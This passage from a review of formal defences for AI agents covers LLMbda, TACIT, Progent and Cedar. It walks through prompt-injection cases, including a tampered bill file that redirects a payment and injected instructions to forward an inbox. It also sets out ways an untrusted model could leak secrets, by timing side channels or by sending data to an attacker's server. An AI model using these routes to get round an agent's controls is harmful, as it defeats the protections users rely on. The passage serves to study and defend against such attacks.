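Strict checks would also stop the program that replies to a stranger's email with a category. LLMbda lets a developer override the untrusted label with an explicit operation called `endorse`:

```
send_email "bob@example.com" (endorse [] category) "Acknowledged."
```

The empty brackets stand for the label "trusted and public", but `endorse` can only raise trust, so the result of endorsing a secret is still secret. `endorse` also does nothing in code that runs because of untrusted data, so an attacker cannot inject a program that endorses its own output.

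A second theorem shows that noninterference still holds for secrets in programs that use `endorse`, however often they endorse data and whatever an attacker writes. A mistaken endorsement may let a stranger choose an email's subject line, but it cannot remove the secret label from a bank balance. The tool still has to check that label. The paper's sample `send_email` checks only for trust and would send a trusted message containing a secret, so a tool that handles private data also needs a rule about recipients.

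A developer can limit the damage by endorsing only values from a short fixed list, much as FIDES restricts the type of an untrusted answer. The program has to endorse a copy of the value first, then release the copy only if it matches an entry on the list. If the program tests the untrusted value before endorsing it, everything inside that branch becomes untrusted and `endorse` has no effect. The paper also describes a version of `endorse` that marks its results and refuses to endorse anything derived from them. Neither restriction has its own formal proof yet.

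### Agents that are supposed to reveal private data

Dongol argues that noninterference is too strong for many useful agents. A calendar assistant that tells people when its owner is free reveals private data by design. A developer could write a rule permitting this release, but would need such a rule for every task.

Dongol's alternative compares the agent with an imaginary one that follows the same plan but never obeys untrusted text. The real agent is secure if, for anything an attacker can learn from it, some input to the imaginary agent would have revealed the same thing. Suppose the assistant sends the calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting. An injected instruction to send the calendar then reveals nothing new, because an ordinary meeting request would also have revealed it. But if the assistant obeys an injected instruction to add the owner's password reset code, it reveals something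 no input to the imaginary agent would have, so it isn't secure.

This standard accepts more useful agents, but it applies only to agents that fix their plan before reading anything untrusted. It also covers only leaks, so an agent could meet it and still delete the wrong file. Noninterference for integrity restricts such actions, provided the tools check for trust.

### What the proof covers

Garby and colleagues wrote their definitions, theorems and interpreter in Lean, a programming language that can also check mathematical proofs. Researchers often prove a theorem about a simplified description of a system and then build the system separately, so the two can differ. For example, *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) uses Lean to check theorems about protecting an agent's long-term memory, and separately documents how its Lean model corresponds to the system and where it differs.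 In LLMbda, the theorems are about the same program that calls the language model. Garby and colleagues believe it is the first agent software of which this is true.

To handle a model's unpredictable responses, the proof represents the model as a book that lists a response for every possible call and conversation. Drawing the book at random using the model's probabilities gives the interpreter's results exactly the distribution that the language's definition specifies. For example, suppose a program calls a model twice to flip a coin that lands heads 30 per cent of the time, and returns only the number of heads. Both the definition and the interpreter give 49 per cent for no heads, 42 per cent for one and 9 per cent for two.

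Several parts of a working agent remain outside the proof:

- **The connection to the model.** Ordinary unverified code sends the conversation over the network and returns the response.
- **The model's probabilities.** The result about the interpreter assumes that each response is an independent draw that depends only on the conversation so far.
- **The tools' real effects.** LLMbda treats all tools and data as part of the program. In the experiments, a layer of Python code copied a simulated bank into the program and copied the changes back afterwards.
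- **The labels and checks.** Developers have to label data sources correctly and put the right checks in the tools. LLMbda treats unlabelled data as trusted and public, the same risky default as in Microsoft's Agent Framework.

The theorem also covers only a single run. If other software restarted the agent whenever it stopped, an attacker could learn one bit per run, as with CaMeL.

### Practising before the real run

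Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori in LLMbda. Like CaMeL, it has a model write a program for each task. Models often make mistakes in a language they have never seen, so the agent needs to retry. But an error message from a run on real data could carry an untrusted label. If the model used that message, its next program would be untrusted too, and the tools would block its payments.

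Randori avoids this by first testing the program on invented data. Reading a file returns placeholder text, and payments do nothing. When the program runs without errors, or the agent has used up its retries, the model writes a final version, which the agent runs on the real data. The model may include `endorse` in the program, but it must decide where to put it before reading anything untrusted. The agent cannot repair mistakes that appear only with the real data.

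The researchers tested Randori on AgentDojo's banking tasks with three models, and ran CaMeL on two of them. Each agent attempted 16 tasks three times. The table gives the share completed when nobody was attacking:

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | 75.0% | 75.0% | 64.6% |
| Randori without `endorse` | not tested | 62.5% | 54.2% |
| CaMeL, policy checks off | 66.7% | not tested | 70.8% |
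| CaMeL, policy checks on | 37.5% | not tested | 37.5% |

Randori, which always enforces its labels, scored about as well as CaMeL did with its checks off. Turning the checks on roughly halved CaMeL's score. But with only 16 different tasks, the margins of error are 19 to 27 percentage points either way, so the experiment could easily miss a substantial difference between Randori and the unchecked CaMeL.

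The comparison with the checked CaMeL isn't quite fair either. Even without `endorse`, Randori completed more tasks than CaMeL with its checks on, but Randori's tools have looser policies, which may explain part of the gap.

For the security test, the researchers combined each task with nine attacks and repeated every combination three times with each model, for a total of 1,296 runs. Two attacks succeeded. In about two-thirds of the combinations, the attack needed a tool that a program for the user's task would never call, so writing the program in advance was normally enough to stop it. The remaining combinations were a more serious test of the labels. They accounted for 423 runs and both successes, a success rate of about 0.5 per cent.

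Few attacks succeeded against CaMeL either, even with its checks off. With MiMo-v2.5, it resisted 138 of 141 attacks in the harder group. The benchmark therefore gives only limited evidence of how much the labels contributed.

### How two attacks succeeded despite the proof

Both successful attacks used GPT-5.2 and the same pairing of user task and injected request. The user asked the agent to pay a bill described in a text file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The program read the account details from the file, endorsed them and passed them to the payment tool. Endorsing the details had labelled them as trusted, so they passed the tool's check.

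The attack is consistent with both theorems. Once a program endorses a stranger's data, noninterference no longer guarantees that the stranger cannot influence trusted results. The theorem about endorsement protects only secrets, and the attack needed no secrets to move money.

Removing `endorse` blocks the attack but also blocks payment of the genuine bill, because both account numbers come from the same untrusted file. A short list of permitted values would not help unless the user already knew whom to pay. According to Garby and colleagues, the same kind of attack succeeded in CaMeL's original evaluation, and CaMeL's developers placed it outside the threats they meant to stop. The user had asked the agent to pay whatever bill the file contained, so anyone who could edit the file could choose the recipient.

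## Permissions checked by a compiler: the TACIT framework

LLMbda checks labels while a program runs, so it may stop a program partway through. A compiler can check the whole program before it runs. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes a framework built on this idea at EPFL in Lausanne, called TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types). The agent writes a short program in Scala, a language that Odersky designed, instead of calling tools one at a time. TACIT runs the program only if the compiler accepts it.

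Checking a program before it runs matters when the program changes things. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), a later paper from the same group, gives the example of a program that subtracts 50 from a balance of 100 and has an error in its next line. In a language that finds such errors only at run time, the subtraction would happen before the error appeared. The Scala compiler rejects both lines together, so the balance stays at 100.

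### Types that list permissions

TACIT controls access with capabilities, as in Hardy's remedy for the confused deputy. Suppose `out` is a capability for one file. This line defines a function that writes text to the file:

```
val save = (text: String) => out.write(text)
```

The compiler works out that the function's type is `String ->{out} Unit`. The function takes a `String`, `Unit` means it returns nothing useful, and the braces list the capabilities it can reach. If a second function calls `save`, the compiler records that the caller can reach `out` too.

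| Type | Capabilities the function may reach |
|---|---|
| `String -> Unit` | none |
| `String ->{out} Unit` | only `out` |
| `String => Unit` | any |

A function of the first type is pure, meaning it can compute a result but cannot write a file, send a message or have any other side effect.

A library can require a function of a particular type. Let C be the set of capabilities the function can reach and D the set the library permits. In the simplest case, the compiler accepts the function if C ⊆ D. When the library requires a pure function, D is empty, so C must be empty too.

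C is an upper bound. It includes capabilities in branches that may never run, so the compiler sometimes rejects a harmless program. But the bound holds for every input, including those no tester would have tried.

### Secrets in a wrapper

Suppose a company's agent runs on a model hosted by another firm and works in a folder containing passwords and confidential contracts. The company wants the agent to process these files without revealing their contents to the other firm. TACIT therefore treats the main model as untrusted and hides secrets from it, whereas FIDES treats the main model as trusted and hides strangers' text from it.

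The owner marks certain paths as classified. A program that reads a file there receives a `Classified[String]`, a sealed wrapper around the text. To work on the contents, it uses a method called `map`:

```
def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`map` applies the function `op` to the contents and seals the result in a new wrapper. The thin arrow means that `op` must be pure. The compiler therefore accepts the first of these lines and rejects the second:

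```
secret.map(text => text.trim)          // accepted
secret.map(text => out.write(text))    // rejected
```

The first function removes spaces from the ends of the text and uses no capability. The second has the type `String ->{out} Unit`, but `map` requires a function with nothing in the braces. The error message identifies `out` as the problem, which helps the model correct its program. The compiler also rejects printing inside `map`, because printing requires a capability for input and output.

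This rule also prevents the leak that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL, where a program reveals private data through the branch it takes. In TACIT, a program can test a wrapped bank balance only inside `map`, and the result is a wrapped yes or no that an `if` statement outside `map` cannot read. Changing an outside variable from inside `map` counts as a side effect, so the compiler rejects it.

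TACIT provides a function called `chat` for tasks such as summarising a contract, which simple pure functions that trim or sort text cannot do. It sends wrapped text to a second, trusted model on the company's own computer and wraps the answer. To report what changed between two versions of a contract, the agent can compute the differences inside `map`, pass them to the local model and save the summary in a classified file. The main model writes the program but never reads the contracts or the summary.

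### Access that ends with a block

A program gets access to a folder by opening a block:

```
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  access("/project/README.md").read()
}
```

`requestFileSystem` creates a capability for the folder, and only the code in the block between the braces can use it. The block can return a file's text but not a way to read more files later. If the block returned a function that reads a file, that function's type would include the folder's capability. The capability doesn't exist outside the block, so the type of the block's result cannot include it, and the compiler rejects the program. TACIT has similar blocks for running commands and reaching websites.

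Some checks have to wait until the program runs. A program may compute a file's path while running, so the library checks then whether the path is inside the folder.

The agent also chooses which folder to request, so a hostile model could request the whole disk. Glama's *TACIT*, a copy of the project's newer documentation, describes a setting that lets the owner put an outer limit on folders. The default limit is the folder where the owner started TACIT.

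### Separate output for the user and the model

A program's printed output goes to both the user and the main model, but wrapped values look different to each:

| The program prints | The user receives | The main model receives |
|---|---|---|
| `2 + 2` | 4 | 4 |
| `summary` (wrapped) | the text of the summary | `Classified(****)` |
| `summary.map(_.length)` | the summary's length | `Classified(****)` |

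A wrapped value can last from one message to the next, although access to the folder cannot. The user can ask a follow-up question about the summary, and the agent can compute the answer without reading it. If the user pastes the summary into the next message, however, the main model receives it as ordinary text and the protection is lost.

The main model also can't detect a poor summary or change its plan based on what a contract says. VirtusLab, a company that helps maintain Scala, warns in *Safe Scala an introduction* that an agent becomes much less useful if its owner classifies too much data.

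### What has to work correctly

Odersky and colleagues name four trusted parts:

- the Scala compiler
- TACIT's library, which defines the wrapper and the blocks
- the runtime, which runs the accepted programs
- the local model, if the owner uses one

The trusted base excludes the main model, the programs it writes and any outside text it reads. The local model's service must also retain nothing from each text after answering, because otherwise a later answer could reveal an earlier secret. The types cannot enforce this, so whoever sets up the service has to ensure it.

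Ordinary Scala has features that override the type checker. With an unchecked cast, for example, a programmer can declare that a value has a different type, which could remove a capability from the braces. In *Scala 3.8.3 is now available!*, Mazur announced an experimental "safe mode" that forbids such features. A program in safe mode can use only libraries that also follow the rules or that a programmer has marked `@assumeSafe`, a claim the compiler does not verify. Scala's *Safe Mode* gives the example of an email function that wraps an unrestricted mailer and asks the user to confirm each message. The programmer vouches for the safety of that function.

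Before TACIT used the compiler's safe mode, a separate program searched the agent's code for forbidden patterns, according to lampepfl's *TACIT*, the project's GitHub page. A list of patterns offers weaker protection because an attacker needs only one dangerous feature that the list omits. The newer documentation describes safe mode as on by default in one place and optional in another, so an owner should turn it on explicitly.

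A program could reveal something about a secret by throwing an exception (an error that interrupts the program) for some values of the secret but not others. Scala's developers decided that tracking every possible exception in types would be too cumbersome, so TACIT catches exceptions at run time and turns them into ordinary values, which it can wrap.

Researchers have proved parts of the type system correct. *Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) includes a Lean-checked proof for a small language modelled on Scala's capability types. *System Capybara* (2026) proves further properties for another small language, which omits classes and exceptions, both common in real Scala programs. Neither proof covers the compiler, whereas the LLMbda theorems apply to the interpreter that runs the agent. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that safe mode still needs its own proof.

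The owner also has to switch off the agent's built-in tools for files, commands and web pages. TACIT works with existing agents such as Claude Code through MCP, and an agent that keeps these tools can bypass the compiler.

### A test with planted secrets

Odersky and colleagues built a small software project with a folder of passwords and confidential documents to test whether an agent would reveal any of them. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 prompt injections, for 120 trials. The injections included fake error messages that demanded a password and ready-made Scala code for reading the secret files. In 11 more trials, the user asked for the secrets directly or by posing as someone with authority, such as a system administrator.

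The researchers ran all 131 trials with two models, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5, first with the secrets wrapped and then with the secrets as plain text. The table gives the share of trials without a leak:

| Trials | Wrapped, both models | Plain text, Sonnet 4.6 | Plain text, MiniMax M2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| 120 with injections | 100% | 100% | 97.5% |
| 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% | 27.3% |
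| All 131 | 100% | 98.5% | 91.6% |

The totals make the unprotected agents look safer than they were, because most trials used injections that both models usually resisted. When the user asked for the secrets, MiniMax M2.5 revealed them in 8 of 11 trials.

Wrapping the secrets did not reduce the number of ordinary tasks the agents completed. Sonnet 4.6 completed 99.2 per cent with wrapping and 83.3 per cent without it, while MiniMax M2.5 completed 90.0 per cent with wrapping and 88.3 per cent without it. The researchers suspect that Sonnet's gain is partly an artefact of the test. Without wrapping, it often ran out of time or turns, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection.

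Eleven trials without a leak are, on their own, consistent with a leak rate of up to about 24 per cent. The argument from the types is much stronger evidence, and the test mainly shows that the implementation has no obvious hole. The test also checked only the one property that the wrapper enforces, so a false summary or a damaged file would not have counted as a leak. The attacks targeted the model, but a determined attacker would also look for bugs in the compiler and the library.

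### Results on AgentDojo

The researchers also adapted AgentDojo's four environments to TACIT and ran about 1,900 attacks across two models. One counted as a success under the benchmark's scoring. A user had asked the agent to book a hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for a second hotel in the reviews of the first. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, and the scoring was based on whether the second hotel's name appeared. TACIT's rules allow public reviews to reach the user, so the type check did not fail.

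The share of tasks completed varied more. The researchers took the CaMeL figures from that system's own paper:

| Environment | TACIT, Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL, Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT, o4-mini | CaMeL, o4-mini |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 56.9% | 52.8% | 59.0% | 62.5% |
| Workspace | 50.5% | 53.8% | 52.9% | 81.4% |
| Slack | 40.0% | 48.6% | 47.6% | 68.6% |
| Travel | 64.3% | 1.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% |

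Odersky and colleagues describe the two systems as comparable, which is generous in the case of o4-mini. With that model, TACIT's completion rate was 29 percentage points lower than the other system's on the office tasks and 21 points lower on the Slack tasks.

It is also unclear how much the types contributed to security. The functions for sending money and email list no capability, and the instructions to the model mention side effects inside `map`. The compiler therefore seems to have let programs use wrapped text in payments and messages. The protection more likely came from wrapping emails, files and reviews, so that the main model never read the injected instructions.

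When Zhao and colleagues ran the same tasks on LACUNA, 8 of about 1,900 attacks succeeded. LACUNA gives each agent only the capabilities its task needs, but an injection can still cause the model to misuse one of them, for example by sending the wrong email when the task requires sending email.

### The cost of writing typed programs

Odersky and colleagues used τ²-bench, which simulates customer service for an airline and a shop, to test whether writing Scala makes agents worse at their work. They compared TACIT with ordinary tool calls on three models, and TACIT scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher every time. They credit the compiler's error messages and the structured data that the Scala functions return.

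On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems from GitHub, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7 per cent with TACIT and 43.3 per cent without it, a difference of five problems. The researchers think ordinary shell commands suit this kind of work better.

On τ²-bench, between 0.3 and 7.9 per cent of programs failed to compile or run at first, depending on the model and the environment, and the agent usually fixed them within one or two tries. Compiling took less than a second once the system had warmed up. *What's in the Box* (2025) reports that capability checking took less than 15 per cent of the time needed to compile Scala's standard library.

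These results show how writing Scala affects the agent's performance, but not how hiding data does, because the airline and shop functions returned ordinary, unwrapped records and the agent could read everything it needed. The AgentDojo scores are a better guide to how the wrapper affects useful work.

The later results for LACUNA are less favourable. Across a wider set of environments, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0 per cent of τ²-bench tasks with LACUNA and 90.0 per cent with ordinary tool calls. The compiler rejected 22.4 per cent of that model's programs for the shop, and 89 per cent of the programs that a weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, wrote for a telephone company. The model's task is harder in LACUNA because its code also controls the agent's loop, so these figures don't apply directly to TACIT. Zhao and colleagues suspect that part of the difficulty comes from models being trained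 on less Scala than Python.

Somebody also has to write the library. The shared part is about 1,000 lines of Scala. Each new set of tools needs its own Scala description, and those for the airline and the shop were a few hundred lines each.

### Leaks and mistakes that compile

A pure function has no side effects, but it still takes time to run. A hostile model could pass `map` a function that runs for ten seconds if the first bit of a secret key is 1 and finishes immediately if it is 0. The compiler would accept the function, and the delay could reveal the bit to the model. Repeating this for each bit would recover a 128-bit key in 128 runs. Odersky and colleagues leave such timing channels outside their guarantee.

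The types also stop applying when a Scala program starts another program. If the owner lets the agent run Python, the Python code can do whatever the operating system allows. Odersky and colleagues recommend permitting only specific, safe commands and adding a sandbox, which limits the files and network connections a process can use.

A newer feature creates a more direct risk. According to Glama's copy of the documentation, a program can now send a wrapped secret to a permitted website, for example to log in with a password that the main model cannot read. If the owner has not set a list of permitted sites, the program may reach any site it requests. As documented, a hostile model could then request access to an attacker's server and send the secret there. The original paper's library did not have this feature, so the 131 trials did not test it.

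The compiler also does not check whether an action is correct. An agent with permission to cancel reservations can cancel the wrong reservation in a program that compiles without errors.

The wrapper protects secrecy but not integrity. An agent can wrap any text and write it over a classified file. The documentation warns that an agent could replace the file listing who may log in to a computer, which could let an attacker in without revealing any secret. The owner can turn off writing to classified files, but it is on by default.

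### Types that record where data came from

Types can protect integrity too, if they record where data came from. *Language-Based Agent Control* does this in Haskell, another language with a strict type system. In its main example, an agent compiles a bibliography that may include only entries from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The function that fetches an entry returns a `Trusted Bib` value, and the function that writes to the bibliography accepts no other type. The library doesn't let the agent create such a value directly, so the agent can get one only by fetching an entry.

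The agent can still use any code to search, sort and choose entries. If it invents a reference and tries to add it, the program doesn't compile. Google's `TrustedSqlString` works the same way. Because an agent may have read hostile text, the Haskell system, like Scala's safe mode, also forbids the language features that bypass the type checker.

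## Permission rules checked at every tool call: Progent and Cedar

Most existing agents call tools one at a time and do not write programs in Scala or LLMbda. The simplest protection to add to such an agent is a rule engine, which is ordinary software that sits between the agent and its tools. The engine compares each call's tool name and arguments with a list of rules and blocks the call unless a rule allows it. Engineers call this "default deny", and it follows Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of fail-safe defaults.

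### One rule and three calls

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, describe a rule engine of this kind and a short notation for its rules. Suppose an agent pays a user's rent, which is £850 a month. The user writes one rule, with a little room for increases:

```
allow send_money when { recipient == "LANDLORD-01" and amount <= 900 }
```

The agent then makes three calls:

| Recipient and amount | Reason for the call | Decision |
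|---|---|---|
| LANDLORD-01, £850 | The user asked the agent to pay the rent | allowed |
| STRANGER-77, £850 | An email contained a hidden instruction | blocked |
| LANDLORD-01, £900 | A forged email announced a rent increase | allowed |

The engine blocks the second call no matter how the email was worded. It allows the third because the recipient and the amount both fit the rule, so the user overpays by £50. The rule would also let the agent pay the rent ten times in one day, because Progent conditions can refer only to the arguments of the current call.

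Checking every call guarantees that calls the rules don't permit never reach a tool, whatever the model does. The trusted base is the engine, the rules and whatever routes the agent's calls through the engine.

### How Progent works

A Progent rule either allows or forbids calls to one tool. Its conditions can compare numbers, look for a value in a list, or match a text pattern. For each call, the engine checks the forbid rules for that tool first and then the allow rules, and blocks the call if no rule matches. After blocking a call, it can stop the agent, ask the user, or return an error message. It usually returns a message that gives the reason and repeats the user's request, so the agent can try another way.

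Developers can add Progent to an agent as a library with a few lines of code. Users who cannot change the agent's code, as with a closed-source product, can run Progent as a proxy, a separate server that forwards the agent's model requests and MCP calls. The proxy cannot check the agent's built-in tools that do not use MCP.

Different requests need different rules. Sending email is necessary when the user asks the agent to write to Alice, but dangerous when the user only wants a summary of unread mail. Progent therefore has a language model write a new set of rules, called a policy, for each request. At first this model receives only the request and the list of tools, both of which are trusted. As the agent works, the model can propose changes to the policy after reading the results of tool calls, which may contain injections.

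Shi and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from Alice:

1. The first policy allows only a search for Alice's email.
2. The email asks for a summary of recent mail, posted to the user's Slack account. The model proposes to allow the tools for reading mail and posting on Slack.
3. The agent looks up the user's Slack name, and the model proposes to restrict posts to that name.
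4. One of the recent emails contains a hidden instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger. If the model is fooled, it proposes to allow the tool for sending email.

Progent applies the third change automatically but asks for approval of the second and fourth. To tell them apart, let A(P) be the set of all calls that a policy P allows. A new policy P′ is a narrowing if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P),

and an expansion otherwise. An SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values satisfy a logical formula, searches for a call that P′ allows and P blocks. If the model lowers the rent limit from £900 to £800, no such call exists. If it raises the limit to £1,000, a payment of £950 is one, so the change is an expansion.

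The set of allowed calls can therefore only shrink between approvals, which Shi and colleagues call monotonic confinement. This prevents an injection from giving the agent new permissions without approval. But the second and fourth changes both came from email text, and the solver classifies both as expansions, so whoever approves them has to work out which one is an attack.

An organisation can also write fixed rules by hand. The engine applies these first, and the model's rules cannot override them.

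### What the tests found

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, using GPT-4o to run the agent and write the rules. The attack success rate fell from 39.9 to 1.0 per cent. According to *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026), a paper on a competing system, Progent's developers reported that the share of tasks completed also fell, by about 3 percentage points.

In that test, the researchers approved every expansion automatically to imitate a careless user. This also removed the protection of monotonic confinement, because the set of allowed calls could grow at any time. The 1.0 per cent therefore mainly reflects how well GPT-4o writes rules. In another test, a person reviewed the first policy and every expansion, and no attack succeeded, but the researchers assumed that this reviewer would always reject a malicious address. Only 6 per cent of the model's updates were expansions, so the reviewer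 would have had few decisions to make.

In June 2026, Narisetty and colleagues repeated the test with Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model, as both the agent and the rule writer. They ran 24 AgentDojo tasks three times:

| | No defence | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adapted attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Attacks that succeeded | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |
| User tasks completed during an attack | 45.2% | 27.1% | 25.8% |

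Progent also needed about fifteen times as many model calls per task. The researchers work for LaunchSafe, which sells agent-security tools, although Progent is not its product.

Their adapted attack was weak. It used one handwritten template that described the malicious action as a routine, pre-approved step to try to get the rule writer to allow it. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that the gentler wording also made the agent less likely to obey. The model ignored every injection in the office tasks even without a defence, so the comparison depends on the banking and Slack tasks.

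Ma and colleagues used a stronger attack, in which a language model rewrites the injected text over six rounds, guided by how often each version succeeds. It succeeded 7.7 per cent of the time against Progent with GPT-4o-mini as the agent, compared with 52.4 per cent with no defence. The same method raised attack success against PIGuard, a text filter, from zero to 28.0 per cent. This supports the view that rules on actions are harder to bypass than filters on text, though a 7.7 per cent success rate is still high for an agent that can move money.

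The most damaging results concern useful work. Nearly all AgentDojo tasks let an agent plan its calls from the user's request alone. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) counts only 6 of the 97 tasks that require a change of plan along the way. It introduces a harder benchmark of 60 tasks in shopping, GitHub and daily life, with 560 attack cases. Every task requires the agent to revise its plan and includes a legitimate instruction from a third party, such as a checkout page's request to log in first. The average task takes 7.1 steps, about twice as many as in AgentDojo.

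| Model | Tasks completed, no defence | Tasks completed, Progent | Attack success, no defence | Attack success, Progent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 53.3% | 6.7% | 37.8% | 1.7% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 51.7% | 25.0% | 20.6% | 1.6% |
| Claude Sonnet 3.5 | 60.0% | 13.3% | 11.9% | 0.0% |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10.0% | 3.3% | 11.9% | 0.5% |

The columns for completed tasks come from runs without attacks. With GPT-4o, the agent finished 32 of the 60 tasks without Progent and 4 with it. Li and colleagues found that the rule writer struggled to assign the right permissions when there were many tools. Its mistakes accumulated over a long task until the policy blocked almost every useful tool, which leaves an agent that resists attacks mostly because it can do very little.

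Three of these researchers also helped develop DRIFT, a rival system that completed 30.0 per cent of the tasks with GPT-4o. Ma and colleagues, whose team overlaps with theirs, found the same problem with two other models, which completed fewer than 7 per cent of AgentDyn's tasks under Progent.

### Cedar

Progent's developers designed their notation for agents. Companies that already control what employees and programs may do can instead reuse an existing authorization language, such as Cedar, which Amazon Web Services released as open source. A request in Cedar identifies a principal (who is acting), an action, a resource and a context, which can hold the arguments of a tool call. The rent rule looks like this:

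```
permit (
  principal == Agent::"assistant",
  action == Action::"send_money",
  resource == Account::"household"
) when {
  context.recipient == "LANDLORD-01" && context.amount <= 900
};
```

It gives the same answers as the Progent rule for all three calls. Cedar also denies by default, and a matching `forbid` rule overrides any `permit` rule.

Cedar's main advantage is how much an administrator can check before the rules take effect. The administrator first writes a schema, which lists the kinds of principal, action and resource and their attributes. A validator then checks every rule against the schema (*AutoCedar*, 2026). If somebody misspells `context.amount` as `context.amont`, the validator reports the mistake before any agent runs.

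Cedar's rules also have a meaning precise enough for software to compare whole policies, according to *From Intent to Execution Grant* (Wu, Zhang and colleagues, 2026). If an administrator rewrites twenty rules as five, an equivalence analysis can determine whether both versions give the same answer to every possible request.

Cedar's developers can prove statements about all requests using a model of the language written in Lean, for example that Cedar never allows a request unless some `permit` rule matches it. The engine that makes the actual decisions is a separate program, handwritten in Rust. *Access Control as Verified Parse Constraints* (2026) describes how the developers connect the two by differential random testing, which gives both the same random inputs and compares their answers. The evidence that the proofs apply to the running software therefore comes from testing, though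 the program is small and deterministic and can be tested on a great many cases.

*LEANGUARD* (2026) avoids that gap by writing the rules in Lean, so the proofs are about the same code that checks the calls, as in LLMbda. Its rules can also use a journal of earlier events and a copy of the company's records. For example, a shop's rule might require that an order belongs to the logged-in customer. The engine checks this in the shop's records and does not accept text from a tool's output as evidence.

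*Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (2026) applies Cedar to agents. A language model writes the rules from the developer's standing instructions to the agent, the company's policy documents, and the MCP definitions of the agent's tools. An ordinary program builds the schema from the tool definitions, so the validator can reject a rule that refers to a tool or argument that does not exist. The model revises the rules until they meet a set standard in further checks. The rules are written before the agent reads a stranger's email, so an injection in that email cannot influence them, a protection that Progent's updates lack.

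### Mistakes in the rules

No validator can confirm that a rule expresses what the company wanted. Yu and colleagues at the company Corners had a language model turn written policies into rules for τ²-bench's airline and retail domains, and examined the errors. One policy required authenticating the customer before any action. The model turned this into a rule that blocked every tool, including the two that perform the login, until the customer had logged in. Another rule would have required the customer's confirmation just to check the status of a flight.

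Their system, NOMOS, finds many such errors by comparing each rule with the definitions of the tools. It repaired or rejected 37 per cent of the rules proposed for the airline and 13 per cent of those for the shop. A stronger model made some of the same kinds of mistake, and six of its rules referred to arguments their tools did not have.

Other rules refer to real tools and arguments but still block legitimate work. To find these, the researchers replayed recorded conversations in which an unprotected agent had done its job correctly. One rule would have refused 95.9 per cent of the calls it applied to. With the corrected rules in place, the share of consequential calls that broke the written policy fell from 66.3 to 2.6 per cent for the airline agent and from 30.8 to 6.9 per cent for the shop agent.

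People who write rules by hand miss cases too. Default deny makes a missing permission fairly harmless, but it doesn't protect against a permission that is too broad. If a user leaves the recipient out of the rent rule, the agent can send £900 to anyone. Legitimate payments will still go through, so they won't reveal the mistake.

A company can write all its permission rules in advance, which keeps untrusted text from influencing them, or let a model revise them as the agent learns more. It is hard to write rules in advance for tasks that change halfway through, such as those in AgentDyn. A model can revise the rules to fit such tasks, but then somebody has to judge each expansion of the agent's permissions. If that person approves expansions without reading them, the agent has little protection beyond the model's own resistance to prompt injection.

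### Where the arguments came from

A rule on a tool call's arguments checks a value but not where it came from. This matters because users often leave values for the agent to find. Ma and colleagues classified 57 AgentDojo tasks. In 36 of them, the user specifies the action but leaves at least one detail, such as the recipient or the amount, to be read from a file or message. A policy based on the user's request cannot specify those missing details.

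Yu and colleagues reran Progent on AgentDojo's banking tasks with an open model, Gemma 4. Attack success fell from 46.5 to 5.6 per cent, and the share of tasks completed when there was no attack fell from 79.2 to 62.5 per cent. All sixteen remaining successes came from four tasks in which the user did not give the recipient's account number, so the policy had to allow any recipient, including the attacker. Nine of them involved a request to pay a bill "like last month", and three involved the bill in a text file that also defeated the LLMbda agent.

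NOMOS blocked these attacks with a rule that the agent may pay only accounts that the user has named or that appear in the transaction history. No payment reached the attacker's account, but the rule also blocked the genuine bill, because its account number appears only in the file. In 8 of 288 attack cases, the agent sent an injected payment to somebody the user had paid before, which the rule permits. When there was no attack, NOMOS completed 70.8 per cent of tasks, more than Progent, but the difference could be due to chance because there were only 16 tasks.

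To apply a rule about origin, the engine needs a reliable record of where each value came from. If an account number appears verbatim in the user's request, a text search can find it. Narisetty and colleagues point out that tracing a value is much harder when the model has summarised or combined several texts, because software that handles only tool calls and their results cannot observe how the model arrived at an argument. FIDES deals with this by assuming that everything in the conversation influenced the model's output, which is safe but blocks more work.

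Several of the researchers who tested Progent with the rewritten attacks also built ROPE, which tracks the origin of only the most sensitive arguments. In their tests, ROPE kept attack success low without the large loss of completed tasks that Progent had on AgentDyn. An independent test would be more convincing.

### The same effect by another route

Rules on tool calls work best when each tool does one clear thing, but many coding agents have a single tool that runs any command the model writes. The benchmark in *INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, 2026) is built around such an agent, which reads files, installs software and contacts websites through the same tool. A rule that allows or forbids this tool by name can only permit every command or none. A rule on the tool's argument has to interpret the command, and there are usually many ways to write a command that does the same thing.

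Progent also cannot check the clicks of agents that operate a computer through its screen, because its rules apply to text arguments and a click is only a position on the screen.

*Cross-Interface Authorization for AI Computer-Use Agents* (Zhu and Wang, 2026) examines what happens when an agent can reach the same effect in several ways. In its example, an agent has permission to give somebody read access to a code repository. The dialog box checks this permission, but a command with the same effect reaches the database without being checked, so an agent that fails at the dialog box can use the command instead. This breaks Anderson's second condition for a reference monitor, that the check must always be invoked.

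Checking both routes with the same rule engine is not quite enough. The dialog box might grant read access by default while the command grants write access, so an approval given for one could authorize something different through the other. The repository's name might also start to refer to a different repository after the approval but before the action. Wu and colleagues, who work for a security company, point out that in authorization languages generally, a decision to allow a request does not by itself specify when that decision expires, or whether it still applies if the agent later changes the request.

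Zhu and Wang propose the following procedure:

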